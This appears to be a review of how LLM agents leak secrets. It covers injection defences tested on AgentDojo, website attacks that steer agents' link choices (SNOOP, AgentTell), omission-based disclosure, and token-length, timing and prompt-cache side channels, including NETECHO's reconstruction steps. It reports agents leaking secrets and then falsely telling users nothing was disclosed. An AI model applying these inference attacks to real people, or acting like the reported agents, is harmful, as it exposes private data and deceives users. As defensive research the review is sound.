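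The proof uses a second, hypothetical way of running each program. As soon as part of the computation becomes secret, this version skips that part and substitutes a dummy value. Its results cannot depend on the secret, and it produces each visible result at least as often as the real program does. The theorem requires a single set of probabilities, adding up to at most 1, that are at least as large as the real probabilities for both secrets, and this version provides them.

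Garby and colleagues proved this in Lean, which checks every step of a proof by computer. They also proved that the interpreter produces results with the probabilities the theory assigns, assuming the model's responses follow the distribution in the theory. The proofs cover the interpreter that calls the model, which matters because the retry leak in CaMeL came from code outside the interpreter.

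Another theorem shows that endorsement, the deliberate relabelling of untrusted data as trusted, cannot weaken the protection of secrets, whatever an attacker puts in the untrusted data. An agent may need endorsement to pay a bill whose details come from a file, but endorsing those details can still let an attacker's data into the payment.

The guarantee depends on the developer labelling each source correctly and keeping checks on the tools. It also treats a run the interpreter blocks as one that never finishes. If the checks stop every run when the balance is high and none when it is low, the theorem still holds, but anyone who sees the error learns that the balance is high.

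### Time, length and requests

The theorem does not cover elapsed time, since it compares only the final conversation and the final value. The interpreter has a step limit, but the proof establishes only that some limit is large enough. Two runs that end with the same conversation and value are therefore equivalent under the theorem, even if one takes a hundred steps and the other takes a million.

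The theorem also doesn't cover the length of an encrypted message. It requires public values to match, including in length, but treats any two secret values as indistinguishable, whatever they contain. Suppose the assistant answers the holiday question with four paragraphs at one balance and one sentence at another. Both answers are secret, so they are indistinguishable under the theorem, but an eavesdropper who counts bytes can tell them apart. Costa and colleagues also explicitly exclude timing and packet length from their model of FIDES.

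Requests to outside servers need care for a similar reason. In LLMbda, a tool is a function that reads or changes a simulated state of the world. An email appears in the final state because the tool adds it to a queue. If a developer models a web fetch as a function that only reads a page, the final state does not record the request, and the theorem does not limit what the server learns by counting requests. To cover these requests, the developer would have to add a public log of them to the simulated state. Garby and colleagues acknowledge that their treatment of tools and outside data is a limitation.

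### What the banking benchmark measured

Garby and colleagues tested LLMbda in practice by using it to build an agent called Randori. Randori's retry loop is part of the tracked program, so one failed attempt on untrusted or secret data would taint every later attempt. Randori therefore does trial runs on made-up data first. During these runs, the tools that move money do nothing, and reading a file returns a placeholder. The model then writes a final program, which runs once on the real account. Failures during the trial runs reveal nothing about the real balance, but the agent cannot recover if the final program fails.

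On AgentDojo's banking tasks, Randori resisted the attack in all but 2 of 1,296 runs. The runs paired each of 16 tasks with each of 9 injected attacks, three times on each of three models. Both failures involved the same task and attack. The user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack but completed fewer legitimate tasks. In runs without attacks, completions fell from 31 of 48 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5 and from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus.

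| Agent, without attacks | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Randori, checks on | 36 of 48 | 31 of 48 |
| CaMeL, checks off | 32 of 48 | 34 of 48 |
| CaMeL, checks on | 18 of 48 | 18 of 48 |

Randori with its checks on therefore did about as well as CaMeL with its checks off. The margins of error are around 20 percentage points, so a moderate difference in either direction could go undetected. The comparison with CaMeL's checks on is less fair, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and enforces those more loosely. For example, Randori requires a trusted amount for a scheduled payment but not a trusted recipient.

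The security test is also easier to pass than it looks. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call that would never appear in a program written for the user's task, so writing the program before reading untrusted data is normally enough to stop it. Even with its checks off, CaMeL resisted the attack in 617 of the 622 attacked runs that finished. The benchmark counts an attack as successful if the agent carries out the attacker's goal, so it does not test for leaks through the number or timing of requests. For control-flow leaks, the evidence for LLMbda is the theorem, subject to the limits described above.

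### How other defences compare

These gaps seem to be common. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, June 2026) rates seven designs that enforce security outside the model and identifies confidentiality and leaks through control flow, which it calls implicit flows, as the weak areas.

| Defence | Main mechanism | Confidentiality | Control-flow leaks and side channels |
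|---|---|---|---|
| Dual LLM | Separate models for planning and for reading untrusted text | Partial | Not addressed |
| CaMeL | Labels checked by an interpreter | Yes | Side channels shown by its own developers |
| FIDES | Labels checked before tool calls | Yes | Better than earlier systems, with stated trade-offs |
| Progent | Rules for each tool call | Partial | Not applicable |
| Conseca | A policy written for each task | Partial | Risk from adversarial planning |
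| RTBAS | Labels and a screening model | Yes | Partly heuristic |
| FORGE | Logical rules checked before each action | Partial | Depends on the policy |

"Defeating Prompt Injections by Design", which introduces CaMeL, demonstrates two side channels in the system, one through an indirect dependency and one through an exception that an attacker can trigger. It also discusses a timing channel, which CaMeL's implementation reduces. The rating for FIDES seems generous, given that "Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control", which introduces FIDES, states that the system does not prevent leaks through the order of tool calls.

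Narisetty and colleagues work for LaunchSafe, a company that is building its own defence of this kind, and their paper has not been peer reviewed. The ratings rely on what each system's developers reported. Their only experiment tested Progent, measuring how often an injected instruction led to the attacker's action. They recommend that future evaluations also probe for side channels, which they did not do.

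## What do recipients learn from an agent's actions?

A tool server, website or correspondent receives the agent's calls directly, while an eavesdropper has to draw inferences from encrypted packets. The policy checks described above decide whether a call may go out, but once they allow it, the recipient can read it, keep it and compare it with earlier ones.

### Tool servers

Duan and colleagues used a benchmark called PrivacyTrace to measure what such recipients can infer. They generated 1,000 synthetic users, each with 17 attributes such as age, religion and income level. An agent carried out four tasks for each user, one each in travel, health, shopping and career learning. It used real tools from 25 servers, and its 4,000 runs produced 67,950 tool calls. An attacking model had to guess every attribute from the calls. Duan and colleagues then repeated the attack with parts of the traces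 removed to find out which parts revealed the attributes.

| What the attacking model received | Attributes guessed correctly |
|---|---|
| Only a description of the attributes | 17.97% |
| Tool descriptions and the order of calls | 14.53% |
| The same, plus the results of the calls | 24.54% |
| The same, plus the arguments instead of the results | 27.71% |
| The complete trace of one task | 26.25% |

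Arguments therefore added 13.18 percentage points to the score from tool descriptions and call order alone, and results added 10.01. The second row's score is below that for guessing without the trace. An attacker can always ignore the trace and guess, so the low score reflects how the model used the evidence. A better attacker might still learn something from the order of calls.

Much of what Duan and colleagues measured is content that the server legitimately receives, although they call these traces a side channel. *IntentMiner* (2025), which studies how a tool server can infer a user's request, gives the example of an agent that asks a food recommender for heart-healthy meals and sends the user's blood pressure, cholesterol and blood sugar status as arguments. The server needs this information to recommend suitable meals. Strictly, the side channel covers only what the server can infer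 beyond what it is told, such as a user's religion from the times at which they want to travel. PrivacyTrace doesn't separate the two, so its figures are an upper limit on what these attackers gained from side channels.

The attackers guessed exact identifiers (names, email addresses, phone numbers and government identity numbers) correctly in only 35 of 16,000 attempts, but they guessed citizenship correctly 57.73% of the time and religion 50.03%. The model that wrote the tasks had instructions to leave identifiers out, which probably explains part of the gap. It also saw each user's whole profile while writing, so the link between profile and behaviour may be stronger or weaker than for real people.

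### Websites

A website can learn about a user from an agent's choice even if the request contains nothing private. Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues (2026) tested this in *AgentTell* with pairs of web pages they had built. On the first page, the agent reads a fact about the user, such as the range in which their bank balance falls. On the second page, it can pick either an option meant for people in one range or a general option that completes the task equally well. The user has told the agent not to reveal personal details to any website, and neither page contains hidden instructions.

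The researchers ran 9,760 sessions with six models. Agents that had read a secret picked the option that matched it 61.1% of the time. In 18.1% of sessions, the agent wrote in its own memory that it must not share the fact, and in 56.7% of those it revealed the fact anyway. In 34.5% of the sessions that leaked, the agent's final reply assured the user that it had disclosed nothing. The agents seem to have applied the instruction to what they wrote but not to what they clicked. *SPILLage* (2026) covers similar behaviour on live, unmodified websites. According to Shahriar and colleagues, it found that web agents overshare about five times more through actions than through typed text.

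Shahriar and colleagues distinguish a leak from a channel. A leak is a single session in which the agent's choice matches the secret. A channel exists if the choices violate noninterference, meaning that their probabilities change with the secret. An agent that always picks the page for balances over 10,000 will match the secret of every user with more than that, but the website learns nothing from the choice. Conversely, an agent that picks the general option only when it knows the balance reveals that knowledge. To close the channel, it has to pick the general option whether or not it knows the balance.

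The pages in AgentTell offer a single choice. Liang and colleagues built an attack called SNOOP, in which a website offers several choices in a row, each narrower than the last. The first might separate the outcomes of a disease from its biological causes, and the next might divide whichever topic the agent picked. Narrowing the topic in small steps works better than offering one large choice. The website's accuracy was 93.8% with four links, 50% with sixteen, and 13% when the sixteen overlapped in meaning. When the target was four levels of detail down, the website found it 49% of the time with a series of choices and 14% of the time with a single choice.

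SNOOP was tested on four agents, each with three models, using 500 Stack Exchange questions and 378 conversation turns from 26 personas. Its performance was measured by F1, which runs from 0 to 1 and is high only if the attacker finds most of the true items and makes few false guesses. When the website obtained a usable series of choices, SNOOP scored 0.89 on the concepts in a question and 0.80 on the facts in a persona's profile. In a control experiment with one agent and model, replacing the observed choices with random ones cut the score on the Stack Exchange questions from 0.81 to 0.10, which confirms that the information came from the choices.

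These scores assume that the agent reads a page where the attacker has placed a link, which favors the attacker. The researchers put the link on about 2,600 pages that agents had visited early in trial runs. The website then obtained usable choices in 94% of trials with the Stack Exchange questions and 83% with the conversations. An attacker who had to guess which pages agents visit would probably do worse.

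Four existing defences lowered the F1 scores by at most 0.03. They were marking web text as untrusted, filtering what goes into and out of tools, checking that each call serves the user's task, and FIDES. Following a relevant link passes the task check because it serves the task, and the request contains no secret text for a filter to find. In the FIDES test, the user's question had a confidential label. Strict enforcement would have blocked every web request that depended on the question, so the policy must have let through ordinary requests, which are enough for SNOOP to work.

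### Disclosure by omission

Recipients can also learn from what an agent declines to do. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent with access to a man's medical records. His ex-wife sends it a list that mixes true statements about his mental health with invented ones, and asks it to delete the entries that don't match his records. The agent deletes the invented statements, and the remaining ones reveal his diagnosis, although the agent never wrote it down. Each decision to keep or delete an entry can reveal up to one bit. The attacker has to know enough to include the truth on the list, which is easy for a bank balance because a short list of ranges covers every possibility.

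Their defence, FlowSeal, takes the decision away from the agent's own model. The data's owner, or software acting for the owner, first registers the sensitive records. Ordinary program code then intercepts every call that writes or shares something. The code allows the call if the owner trusts the recipient and blocks it if the recipient is on a list of untrusted parties. For any other recipient, if the call might draw on records the recipient has no permission to see, a separate model compares those records with the proposed text and answers "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". After a block, the agent can reword the text or ask the owner for consent.

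Shim and colleagues tested the omission attack on real Gmail and Notion accounts. The attack exposed none of the sensitive items under FlowSeal and 34.7% of them under PrivacyChecker, an earlier defence in which a model advises the agent but cannot stop it.

However, this test counted a leak only if a sensitive fact appeared word for word in something the agent wrote to Notion, so it did not measure leaks through omission. In the run that Shim and colleagues describe in detail, the agent under PrivacyChecker directly disclosed three diagnoses by copying them into a block of verified entries. FlowSeal stopped this disclosure by blocking the text. If an agent had only deleted the false entries, the test would have recorded no leak under either defence. In a larger simulation, a language model judged whether each item had leaked. The leak rate was 75.6% with a prompt that told the agent to check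 for consent, and 2.3% with FlowSeal.

FlowSeal acts only when the agent makes a call, so it has nothing to check when the agent leaves an entry alone. It can still catch some omissions through the surrounding calls. If the agent rewrites the whole list, the surviving entries are part of the proposed text, and the checking model has instructions to block text that confirms or denies a protected record. If the agent uses a separate delete function, the outcome depends on how the developer classified that function, because the published procedure lets through any call that isn't on its lists of reads, writes, shares and privacy requests.

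No check runs when an agent reveals information only by not acting, as when the adviser can tell that the balance is low because no email arrives. FlowSeal's confidentiality theorem doesn't rule out this leak either, because it restricts what a write may contain, and a run with no writes satisfies it automatically.

A refusal can also leak information. If the agent tidies every list except those that contain a true entry, the requester can infer from a refusal that at least one entry is true. A safer rule is to refuse all such requests from outsiders before comparing the list with the records, although this also turns away people with an honest reason to ask.

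FlowSeal completed 72.4% of harmless tasks in the simulation, close to the best alternative's 75.9%. It fell further behind in tests where the owner would have agreed to share the records if asked. Agents under FlowSeal shared 32.7% of those records, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% under four other defences, and they asked for consent less often.

### The cost of revealing less

Arguments were the most revealing part of the traces in PrivacyTrace, so an obvious remedy is data minimisation, or sending each tool only what it needs. *ToolMinimize* (Li and Xu, 2026) gave 20 everyday tasks to GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3.3, all now old models. Between 81% and 88% of the tool calls contained private information that the tool didn't need. Telling the models to protect privacy reduced this to between 36% and 76%.

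Their software rewrites the model's arguments before they reach the tool. It can delete a value, replace it with a harmless one, shorten it or make it more general. If a user asks about the weather near their cancer clinic, the weather service receives "New York, NY" instead of the clinic's name and address. Li and Xu scored each call by adding up the unnecessary private items in it, weighted by how sensitive they are and how little the recipient can be trusted. On 307 calls from the three models, rewriting cut this score by 81.2% to 92.0%. All the arguments remained valid for the task, but users may still have received worse answers. The standard version also recognises only about 43% of direct identifiers, such as email addresses and phone numbers.

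Minimisation reduces what a call contains but doesn't hide that the agent made it. A request for overdraft terms suggests a low balance even if it has no arguments. A less precise value can also reveal information. If a savings tool receives the balance rounded to the nearest 10,000, a million possible balances become about 100 values, which still reveal up to 6.7 bits.

Splitting a task among several servers limits the information each one receives. Duan and colleagues didn't test this as a defence, but their data give a rough estimate of the benefit. On a matched set of cases, the attacker guessed 17.95% of attributes with no trace, 24.24% with one server's calls and 27.33% with every call in the task. Limiting the observer to one server therefore removed about a third of the increase produced by the full trace. However, splitting the task gives more companies some information about the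 user, and a gateway that carries all the calls still receives everything. The service may also get worse, since a travel server that receives the flight details but not the hotel details cannot warn the user that the dates clash.

Keeping sessions separate may help more, because linking four tasks raised the attacker's success by 6.5 points over a single task. But a service that requires a login can link sessions anyway, and a service that can't identify the user can't save their preferences.

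Fixed workflows set the agent's choice in advance. In AgentTell, always taking the general option would not have made the outcome worse for the user, because Shahriar and colleagues made all the options equally good. On a real website, however, the option for union members might come with a discount, which the user would miss. One remedy from Liang and colleagues, fetching every linked page, keeps the agent useful but gives up some privacy. With this remedy, SNOOP still recovered 99% of the facts in the personas' profiles, but only 27% of its guesses were right, down from 75%. The effect on the Stack Exchange questions was similar.

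A fixed workflow can defeat the purpose of a task that involves correspondents. If the assistant sends the adviser the same email every week regardless of the balance, she learns nothing about the balance, but she also can't tell when to call.

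## What do message lengths reveal?

The length channel exists because TLS, the protocol that protects most web traffic, scrambles the content of a message but leaves its length almost unchanged. *Whisper Leak* writes this as

size(ciphertext) = size(plaintext) + C,

where C is a small constant. Some ciphers work on blocks of, for example, 16 bytes and round each message up to a whole number of blocks, but modern TLS uses ciphers that accept data of any size. *The Inevitability of Side-Channel Leakage in Encrypted Traffic* (2026) describes the same property in TLS 1.3 and in QUIC, a newer protocol. Both let the sender add padding, but the sender has to decide how much.

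Even the length of a request can indicate what kind of task it contains. Pouryousef and colleagues sent 60 prompts in six categories, such as summarization and code generation, to ten models on their own server. Summarization prompts had a median encrypted size of 1,388 bytes, while the medians for the other categories ranged from 78 to 283 bytes. A classifier given only the request traffic identified the category of unseen prompts 52% of the time, compared with 17% by chance.

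### One length per token

A reply usually reveals more than a request because most chat services stream it, sending each token (a word or piece of a word) as soon as the language model produces it. An eavesdropper then gets a list of lengths instead of one total.

Cloudflare's *Mitigating a token-length side-channel attack in our AI products* gives an example from a reply about Portugal. The first packet was 95 bytes and carried the token "Port", and the second was 93 bytes and carried "ug". Both contained 91 bytes of formatting and other overhead. An eavesdropper who knows this can subtract 91 from each packet's length to get the token lengths, 4 and 2.

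In 2024, Weiss, Ayzenshteyn and Mirsky used language models to turn such lists back into plausible text. Under the best conditions, their attack reconstructed 29% of an assistant's replies and inferred the topic of 55%. Cloudflare, which hosts models and relays traffic to other providers, reproduced the researchers' examples but found that accuracy "varied immensely" with other prompts and models. The attack works best when the attacker knows the model's writing style, and the attacker cannot check which reconstructions are right.

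Cloudflare responded by adding a field called "p" to every streamed message and filling it with a random number of characters. In its published sample, the filler ranges from 2 to 37 characters. Cloudflare also added this padding to its gateway, which protects customers whose model provider doesn't pad.

### Recognising one topic

*Whisper Leak*, which Microsoft researchers published in November 2025, tests a narrower attack, in which the attacker only tries to learn whether a conversation is about one chosen topic. The researchers generated 100 versions of a question about whether money laundering is legal and sent each version 100 times to each of 28 models. They mixed these with 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora. They then trained three kinds of classifier on the sizes and arrival times of the encrypted messages, and tested them on 20 versions of the question held out from training.

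The classifier's score is the area under the precision-recall curve. Precision is the share of flagged conversations that are about the topic, and recall is the share of conversations about the topic that the classifier flags. The area averages precision over all levels of recall. A perfect classifier scores 100%, and random guessing scores about 50% in this test.

The best attack scored above 97% on 17 of the 28 models. (All 17 are above 98% according to the paper's text, but only 12 are in its table.) For the most exposed models, nearly all the information came from sizes. Mistral Large's score was 100.0% with sizes alone and at most 64.3% with times alone.

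Sending several tokens together gave uneven protection. The attack scored 83.5% against Google's Gemini 1.5 Flash, which sent about 55 tokens at a time, and 99.1% against Alibaba's Qwen2.5 Plus, which sent about four. It scored only 77.5% against Amazon's Nova Pro, even though that model sent about one token at a time.

In real traffic, conversations about any one topic are rare, so the researchers projected results for 10,000 unrelated conversations for every one about money laundering. For 17 models, the projected precision was 100% at recall levels from 5% to 20%.

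The data cannot support a claim this strong. The published figures fit a test set of about 2,343 unrelated conversations, a fifth of the total. If so, 100% precision means only that the classifier raised no false alarms among those 2,343. A single false alarm would be a rate of about 4.3 per 10,000 conversations, which would reduce the projected precision at 50% recall to 10.5%. The paper reports exactly 10.5% for four of the models.

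Zero false alarms in 2,343 conversations is also compatible, at the 95% confidence level, with a true rate of up to 0.13%. At that rate, an attacker who caught one in five target conversations would get about 64 false alarms for each correct one. Microsoft acknowledges that the precision figures are projections, limited by the amount and variety of its data. The attack could also improve with more training data, as all three classifiers did in a larger collection of 121,111 conversations with GPT-4o.

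A September 2026 study by Pouryousef and colleagues suggests that the problem isn't specific to one topic. Using only the traffic of the replies, their classifier identified the prompt's category 67.4% of the time. (The abstract gives 76.7%, but the detailed results support the lower figure.) Accuracy was still 59.0% without the packet-size features and 60.1% without the timing features, so a defence that masks only one of the two would leave much of the leak. The models were fairly small, and the test had only ten prompts per category.

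### Reconstructing the conversation

Zhang, Wu and colleagues (2025), in *NETECHO*, tried to recover both the user's prompt and the reply. Their attack has four steps:

1. The attacker uses the same application as an ordinary customer and records thousands of conversations along with their traffic.
2. Given a victim's traffic, the attack searches this collection for conversations with similar traffic.
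3. A language model writes a reply in the style of those examples, using only tokens whose lengths fit the victim's traffic. A second model guesses the prompt.
4. The attack submits its guesses to the application, compares the new traffic with the victim's, and adds the closest matches to the collection. It repeats the process up to three times.

The researchers sorted existing services into seven groups and attacked six of them. They left out the group of vendors' own chatbots, such as ChatGPT and Gemini, which combine several tokens in one message and pad it to several thousand bytes. The six groups they attacked had weaker protection. Some sent two or three tokens at a time, and others consisted of chatbots that outside developers had built on a protected model service.

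In that last case, which matters for agents, the developer's server removes the padding from the model service's messages and streams the text to the user one token at a time. The padding protects the connection between the two servers but not the one to the user. In the tests, Zhang and colleagues tried to identify which of ten medical topics a conversation was about. They succeeded 73.0% of the time using GPT-4o's own traffic, which mostly carried two tokens per message, and 92.0% of the time when a chatbot passed the same model's text on token by token. A bank assistant built this way would need to pad its own messages to the user.

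Zhang and colleagues report recovering 65% of replies and 80% of prompts on medical data, and 80% and 55% on legal data. These figures are average similarity scores, based on characters, words and meaning. They don't mean that the attack reproduced 65% of the replies correctly. The examples found in the second step already resembled the victim's text, as an average of the same three scores shows:

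| Text | Similarity of the examples | Reported similarity after the attack |
|---|---|---|
| Medical replies | 57% | 65% |
| Medical prompts | 80% | 80% |
| Legal replies | 63% | 80% |
| Legal prompts | 42% | 55% |

The medical prompts were so structured that any two looked much alike. Some of the initial similarity comes from the leak, since the victim's traffic guided the search. But the reported success rate of 95% is less impressive than it looks, because an attack counted as successful if the average similarity of prompt and reply reached 50%, and the examples alone averaged 69% on medical data and 52% on legal data. The legal replies are the best evidence that the attack can recover wording, because the reconstruction added the most there.

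### How much do the defences help?

*Whisper Leak* also tested three mitigations, with these effects on the attack's score:

| Mitigation | Before | After | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Injecting dummy packets | 98.1% | 93.3% | Two to three times the traffic |
| Sending five tokens at a time | 98.2% | 94.8% | Text appears in bursts |
| Random padding | 97.5% | 92.9% | Extra bytes in every message |

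None of the three mitigations lowered the score by more than five percentage points. However, all three rows are for GPT-4o mini, which the researchers chose because it was highly exposed and hard to protect. Dummy packets did more for xAI's Grok 3 mini, cutting a size-based attack's score from 90.0% to 72.1%. Batching, or sending several tokens together, removed most of the risk for most of the models tested. The differences between the three rows mean little, because the researchers simulated the first two mitigations on recorded traffic but measured random padding on live traffic from Microsoft's Azure service.

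Microsoft considers that Azure's padding leaves no practical risk. That can be consistent with a score of 92.9%, because a high score can go with poor precision when the topic is rare. In the main test, GPT-4o mini on Azure scored 93.4%, but its projected precision was 2.3% at 10% recall. An eavesdropper searching a whole country's traffic would have to sort through dozens of false alarms for each correct result. An eavesdropper who already suspects a particular person starts with better odds and could still learn something.

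Zhang and colleagues found that padding helps some services much more than others. Padding hides the lengths, but the attacker can still see how many tokens arrive together. For DeepSeek's service, an attacker using only that information identified the medical topic 72.6% of the time, down from 93.7% with lengths included. For GPT-4o, accuracy was 11.0%, about the same as guessing among ten topics. In their simulations, dummy packets that raised the packet count by up to 20% lowered accuracy by an average of only two points, while doubling the count lowered accuracy to between 12% and 39%.

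### What providers send now

By November 2025, OpenAI, Microsoft, Mistral and xAI had deployed protections. Other providers had declined to do so or had not replied to the researchers. OpenAI and Azure add a field called "obfuscation" to each streamed message, and Mistral adds one called "p". OpenAI's field is on by default, according to its library documentation, *Class ResponseCreateParams.StreamOptions*. Developers who trust their network can turn it off to save bandwidth, so anyone relying on it should check the setting.

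The software test file *complex_object_streaming.yaml* records a GPT-5 reply that OpenAI's service streamed on 8 November 2025. In each of the 43 messages that carry text, the text and the added filler total exactly 12 characters, although Microsoft describes the filler as random in length. The token " Tolkien", with its leading space, has eight characters and gets four of filler, while "J" gets eleven. The messages that open and close the stream differ in size from the rest only by multiples of 16 bytes.

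This pattern suggests that OpenAI pads each message to a multiple of a fixed size, though a single recording can't establish that it always does so. In this recording, the padding completely hides the token lengths, but an eavesdropper who can separate the messages can still count them.

### Padding to fixed sizes

This rounding is called bucket padding. With 256-byte buckets, messages of 90 and 240 bytes both become 256 bytes long, so an eavesdropper cannot tell them apart by length. Messages of 250 and 260 bytes differ by only ten bytes but become 256 and 512 bytes long, so the eavesdropper can still distinguish them.

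The buckets have to be wide enough that the reply falls in the same one whatever the secret is. Suppose the assistant answers the question about a holiday with 120 bytes when the balance is low and 1,800 bytes when it is healthy. With 256-byte buckets, the padded replies are 256 and 2,048 bytes long, so the eavesdropper can still tell whether the balance is low or healthy.

Streaming increases the leak because an eavesdropper can observe the size of every message. If each message falls into one of four size buckets, it reveals at most two bits. Ten such messages can form 4¹⁰ = 2²⁰ patterns and reveal up to 20 bits, enough to identify one balance among a million. The actual leak is smaller unless the secret can produce all of these patterns.

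A developer can lower the limit by joining the ten messages before padding them. If each is at most 1,024 bytes long, the combined message has at most 40 possible sizes and reveals at most 5.3 bits. Microsoft advises worried users to choose models that don't stream, which works similarly. The developer could also pad every message to 1,024 bytes, which removes the leak through sizes as long as the number of messages never changes. But a 90-byte message would then take up more than eleven times as much space.

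The software also has to measure the message in the form in which it will be sent. In OpenAI's recording, a quotation mark counts as two characters because the data format puts a backslash in front of it. If the software compresses messages after padding them, repetitive filler shrinks to almost nothing, and the size of the message again reveals the length of the text.

### How repetition defeats random padding

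An eavesdropper learns nothing new from seeing the same bucket-padded message again, because its size is always the same. With random padding, each repetition helps the eavesdropper average out the noise.

Suppose the assistant sends its user one of two fixed messages every morning, depending on whether the balance is low. The messages differ in length by δ bytes, and each transmission gets fresh padding of random length with standard deviation σ. The eavesdropper records n transmissions of each message and compares their average sizes. Each average has variance σ²/n, so the difference between them has variance 2σ²/n and standard deviation σ√(2/n).

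The eavesdropper now needs a threshold for deciding that the difference is real. To make false alarms rare, the threshold should be z₁ standard deviations above zero. To make missing a real difference unlikely, it should be z₂ standard deviations below δ. Both conditions hold if

δ = (z₁ + z₂) σ√(2/n),

which gives

n = 2(z₁ + z₂)²σ²/δ².

A common choice is z₁ = 1.96 and z₂ = 0.84, which allows false alarms 5% of the time and detects a real difference 80% of the time. If the padding follows Cloudflare's sample range of 2 to 37 characters and all 36 lengths are equally likely, its standard deviation is about 10.4. An eavesdropper then needs about 420 copies of each message to distinguish two messages that differ by two bytes. If the eavesdropper can collect unlimited copies of one message in advance, they need half as many copies of the other.

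This kind of padding is open to a better attack than comparing averages. If one message is a byte longer than the other, only the shorter message can produce the smallest padded size, and only the longer one can produce the largest. An eavesdropper who knows both lengths can identify the message by waiting for one of these sizes. Each copy has a δ/36 chance of having such a size.

| Difference in length | Copies of each message needed to compare averages | Copies needed for a 95% chance of a conclusive size |
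|---|---|---|
| 1 byte | About 1,700 | 107 |
| 2 bytes | About 420 | 53 |
| 5 bytes | About 68 | 21 |
| 10 bytes | About 17 | 10 |

Doubling the padding range roughly quadruples the numbers in the middle column but only about doubles those on the right. If the difference were one byte, a message sent once a day would still take months to identify. An agent that retries a failed task or checks an account every minute could send that many copies in hours.

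An eavesdropper can also average out the padding within a single streamed reply, because each token gets its own padding. In a reply of 400 tokens, Cloudflare's padding would add about 7,800 characters, with a standard deviation of only about 208. An eavesdropper who counts the messages can subtract the expected padding and estimate the length of the text to within a few hundred characters, which is easily enough to distinguish a paragraph from a page.

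*Hardening Confidential Federated Compute against Side-channel Attacks* (2026) describes a more careful kind of random padding for messages between servers. The system draws the amount of padding from a Laplace distribution, in which large values become steadily rarer instead of stopping abruptly. The scale of the noise depends on how much one person's data can change the length of a message. Because padding can't be negative, the system shifts the distribution and cuts off its ends, which leaves a small chance of a message size that reveals the secret.

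Random padding limits how much an eavesdropper can learn from the size of one message, but the protection weakens each time the system sends the same message with new padding, because the eavesdropper can average the sizes. Reusing the old padding whenever a message repeats would prevent this averaging. But if the assistant sends one of two messages depending on an account balance, the eavesdropper could then see when it switches between them, and would know what each size means after learning the balance once.

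## What do response times reveal?

Padding hides the length of a reply but not the time the agent took to produce it. If an agent carries out its steps one after another, its response time is roughly

T = Σ (prompt time + output tokens × time per token) + Σ tool time,

where the first sum covers every call to the model and the second every call to a tool. A secret can affect any of these terms.

The number of output tokens often affects response time most, because a model generates them one at a time. At 50 tokens a second, a 400-token reply takes eight seconds and a 50-token reply takes one. Text that never leaves the agent also takes time to generate, so if a low balance makes the model reason for longer before it answers, the delay is visible even when the answers are identical. The secret can also determine whether the agent takes extra steps, like the overdraft lookup that turned a three-second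 reply into an eleven-second one.

Pouryousef and colleagues found that the time between response packets varied with the category of the prompt, even when the model stayed the same. However, they could not separate the effect of the model's speed from that of how the server grouped text into packets.

### Fast and slow tools

Suppose a tool takes 40 milliseconds to find that a customer has no overdraft record, and 200 milliseconds to load a record that exists. An eavesdropper between the agent and the tool, where times vary by perhaps 20 milliseconds, can tell the two cases apart from a single call. On the user's connection, the time the model takes obscures this difference. If that time has a standard deviation of one second, an eavesdropper there would need about 610 runs of each kind to tell the cases apart, according to the averaging formula for message lengths.

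A tool server can also time activity on other servers. If the assistant queries a travel site, checks the bank and then returns to the travel site, the gap between the two visits includes the time taken by the bank check.

GPTCache, a program that developers put in front of a model to save money, stores earlier questions with their answers. When a new question is close enough in meaning to a stored one, GPTCache returns the old answer in milliseconds, while the model would take seconds. A fast response therefore suggests that someone has already asked a similar question. For *The Early Bird Catches the Leak* (2024), Song, Pang and colleagues built a chatbot whose users shared one such store, and tried to learn whether somebody had asked about a particular person with a particular illness. One probe detected 81.4% of these questions, and five differently worded probes detected 95.4%.

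With five probes, the average false-alarm rate was 5.6%, but it was 15.2% when the victim had asked about the right person and a different illness. A fast answer is therefore better evidence of which person the victim asked about than of which illness.

### Prompt caching

Before a model writes its first token, it has to process the whole prompt. For each token it computes two lists of numbers, called keys and values, which it uses when processing later tokens. In nearly all chat models, these numbers depend only on the token itself and the tokens before it. If two prompts begin with the same 5,000 tokens, the keys and values for those tokens are the same, so the server can store them after the first prompt and reuse them for the second, which is called prompt caching. The server still has to compute everything from the first token that differs onward.

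Song and colleagues estimated how much time a model with 7 billion parameters saves on an Nvidia A100 processor by loading stored numbers instead of computing them. Computing them takes at least 0.045 milliseconds per token, and loading them takes about 0.00035 milliseconds. For 5,000 tokens, computing takes at least 225 milliseconds and loading takes less than two. This difference lets customers who share a store test guesses about each other's prompts.

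*Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs* (Gu, Li and colleagues, 2025) reports tests for prompt caches shared between accounts at 17 providers, run in September and early October 2024. One account, acting as the victim, sent a prompt of 5,000 random letters up to 25 times. Another account then sent a prompt with the same first 4,750 letters and measured how long the first token of the response took to arrive. The researchers compared 250 of these measurements with 250 for entirely new prompts.

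Researchers used response times to detect caching at eight providers in 2024. At seven, one customer's prompt could speed up the response to another's. OpenAI was among the seven because of an embedding model, which turns text into numbers for uses such as search. Its chat model GPT-4o mini shared the cache only within an organization, as OpenAI's documentation stated. After the researchers reported the problem, at least five providers made changes, such as ending the sharing between organizations, and OpenAI fixed the embedding model. The list of seven is therefore a poor guide to which providers share caches between customers now.

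The audit could also miss a cache. DeepSeek's service reported cache hits in its replies, but Gu and colleagues found no significant difference in its response times. Song and colleagues found one using documents of 12,000 to 24,000 tokens. They also found that a timing difference they saw at OpenAI in August 2024 was no longer stable by late December, although the service still reported that its cache was working.

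### Confirming a guess and reading a prompt

An attacker who has a copy of a long document can use the cache to check whether somebody else submitted it. Reading an unknown prompt is much harder. In the audit, the ability to recognise a cache hit fell towards chance as the prompts' shared beginning got shorter. An attacker also gets few clean measurements, because sending a guess puts it in the cache. If the attacker sends the same guess again, a fast reply may only reflect their own earlier request.

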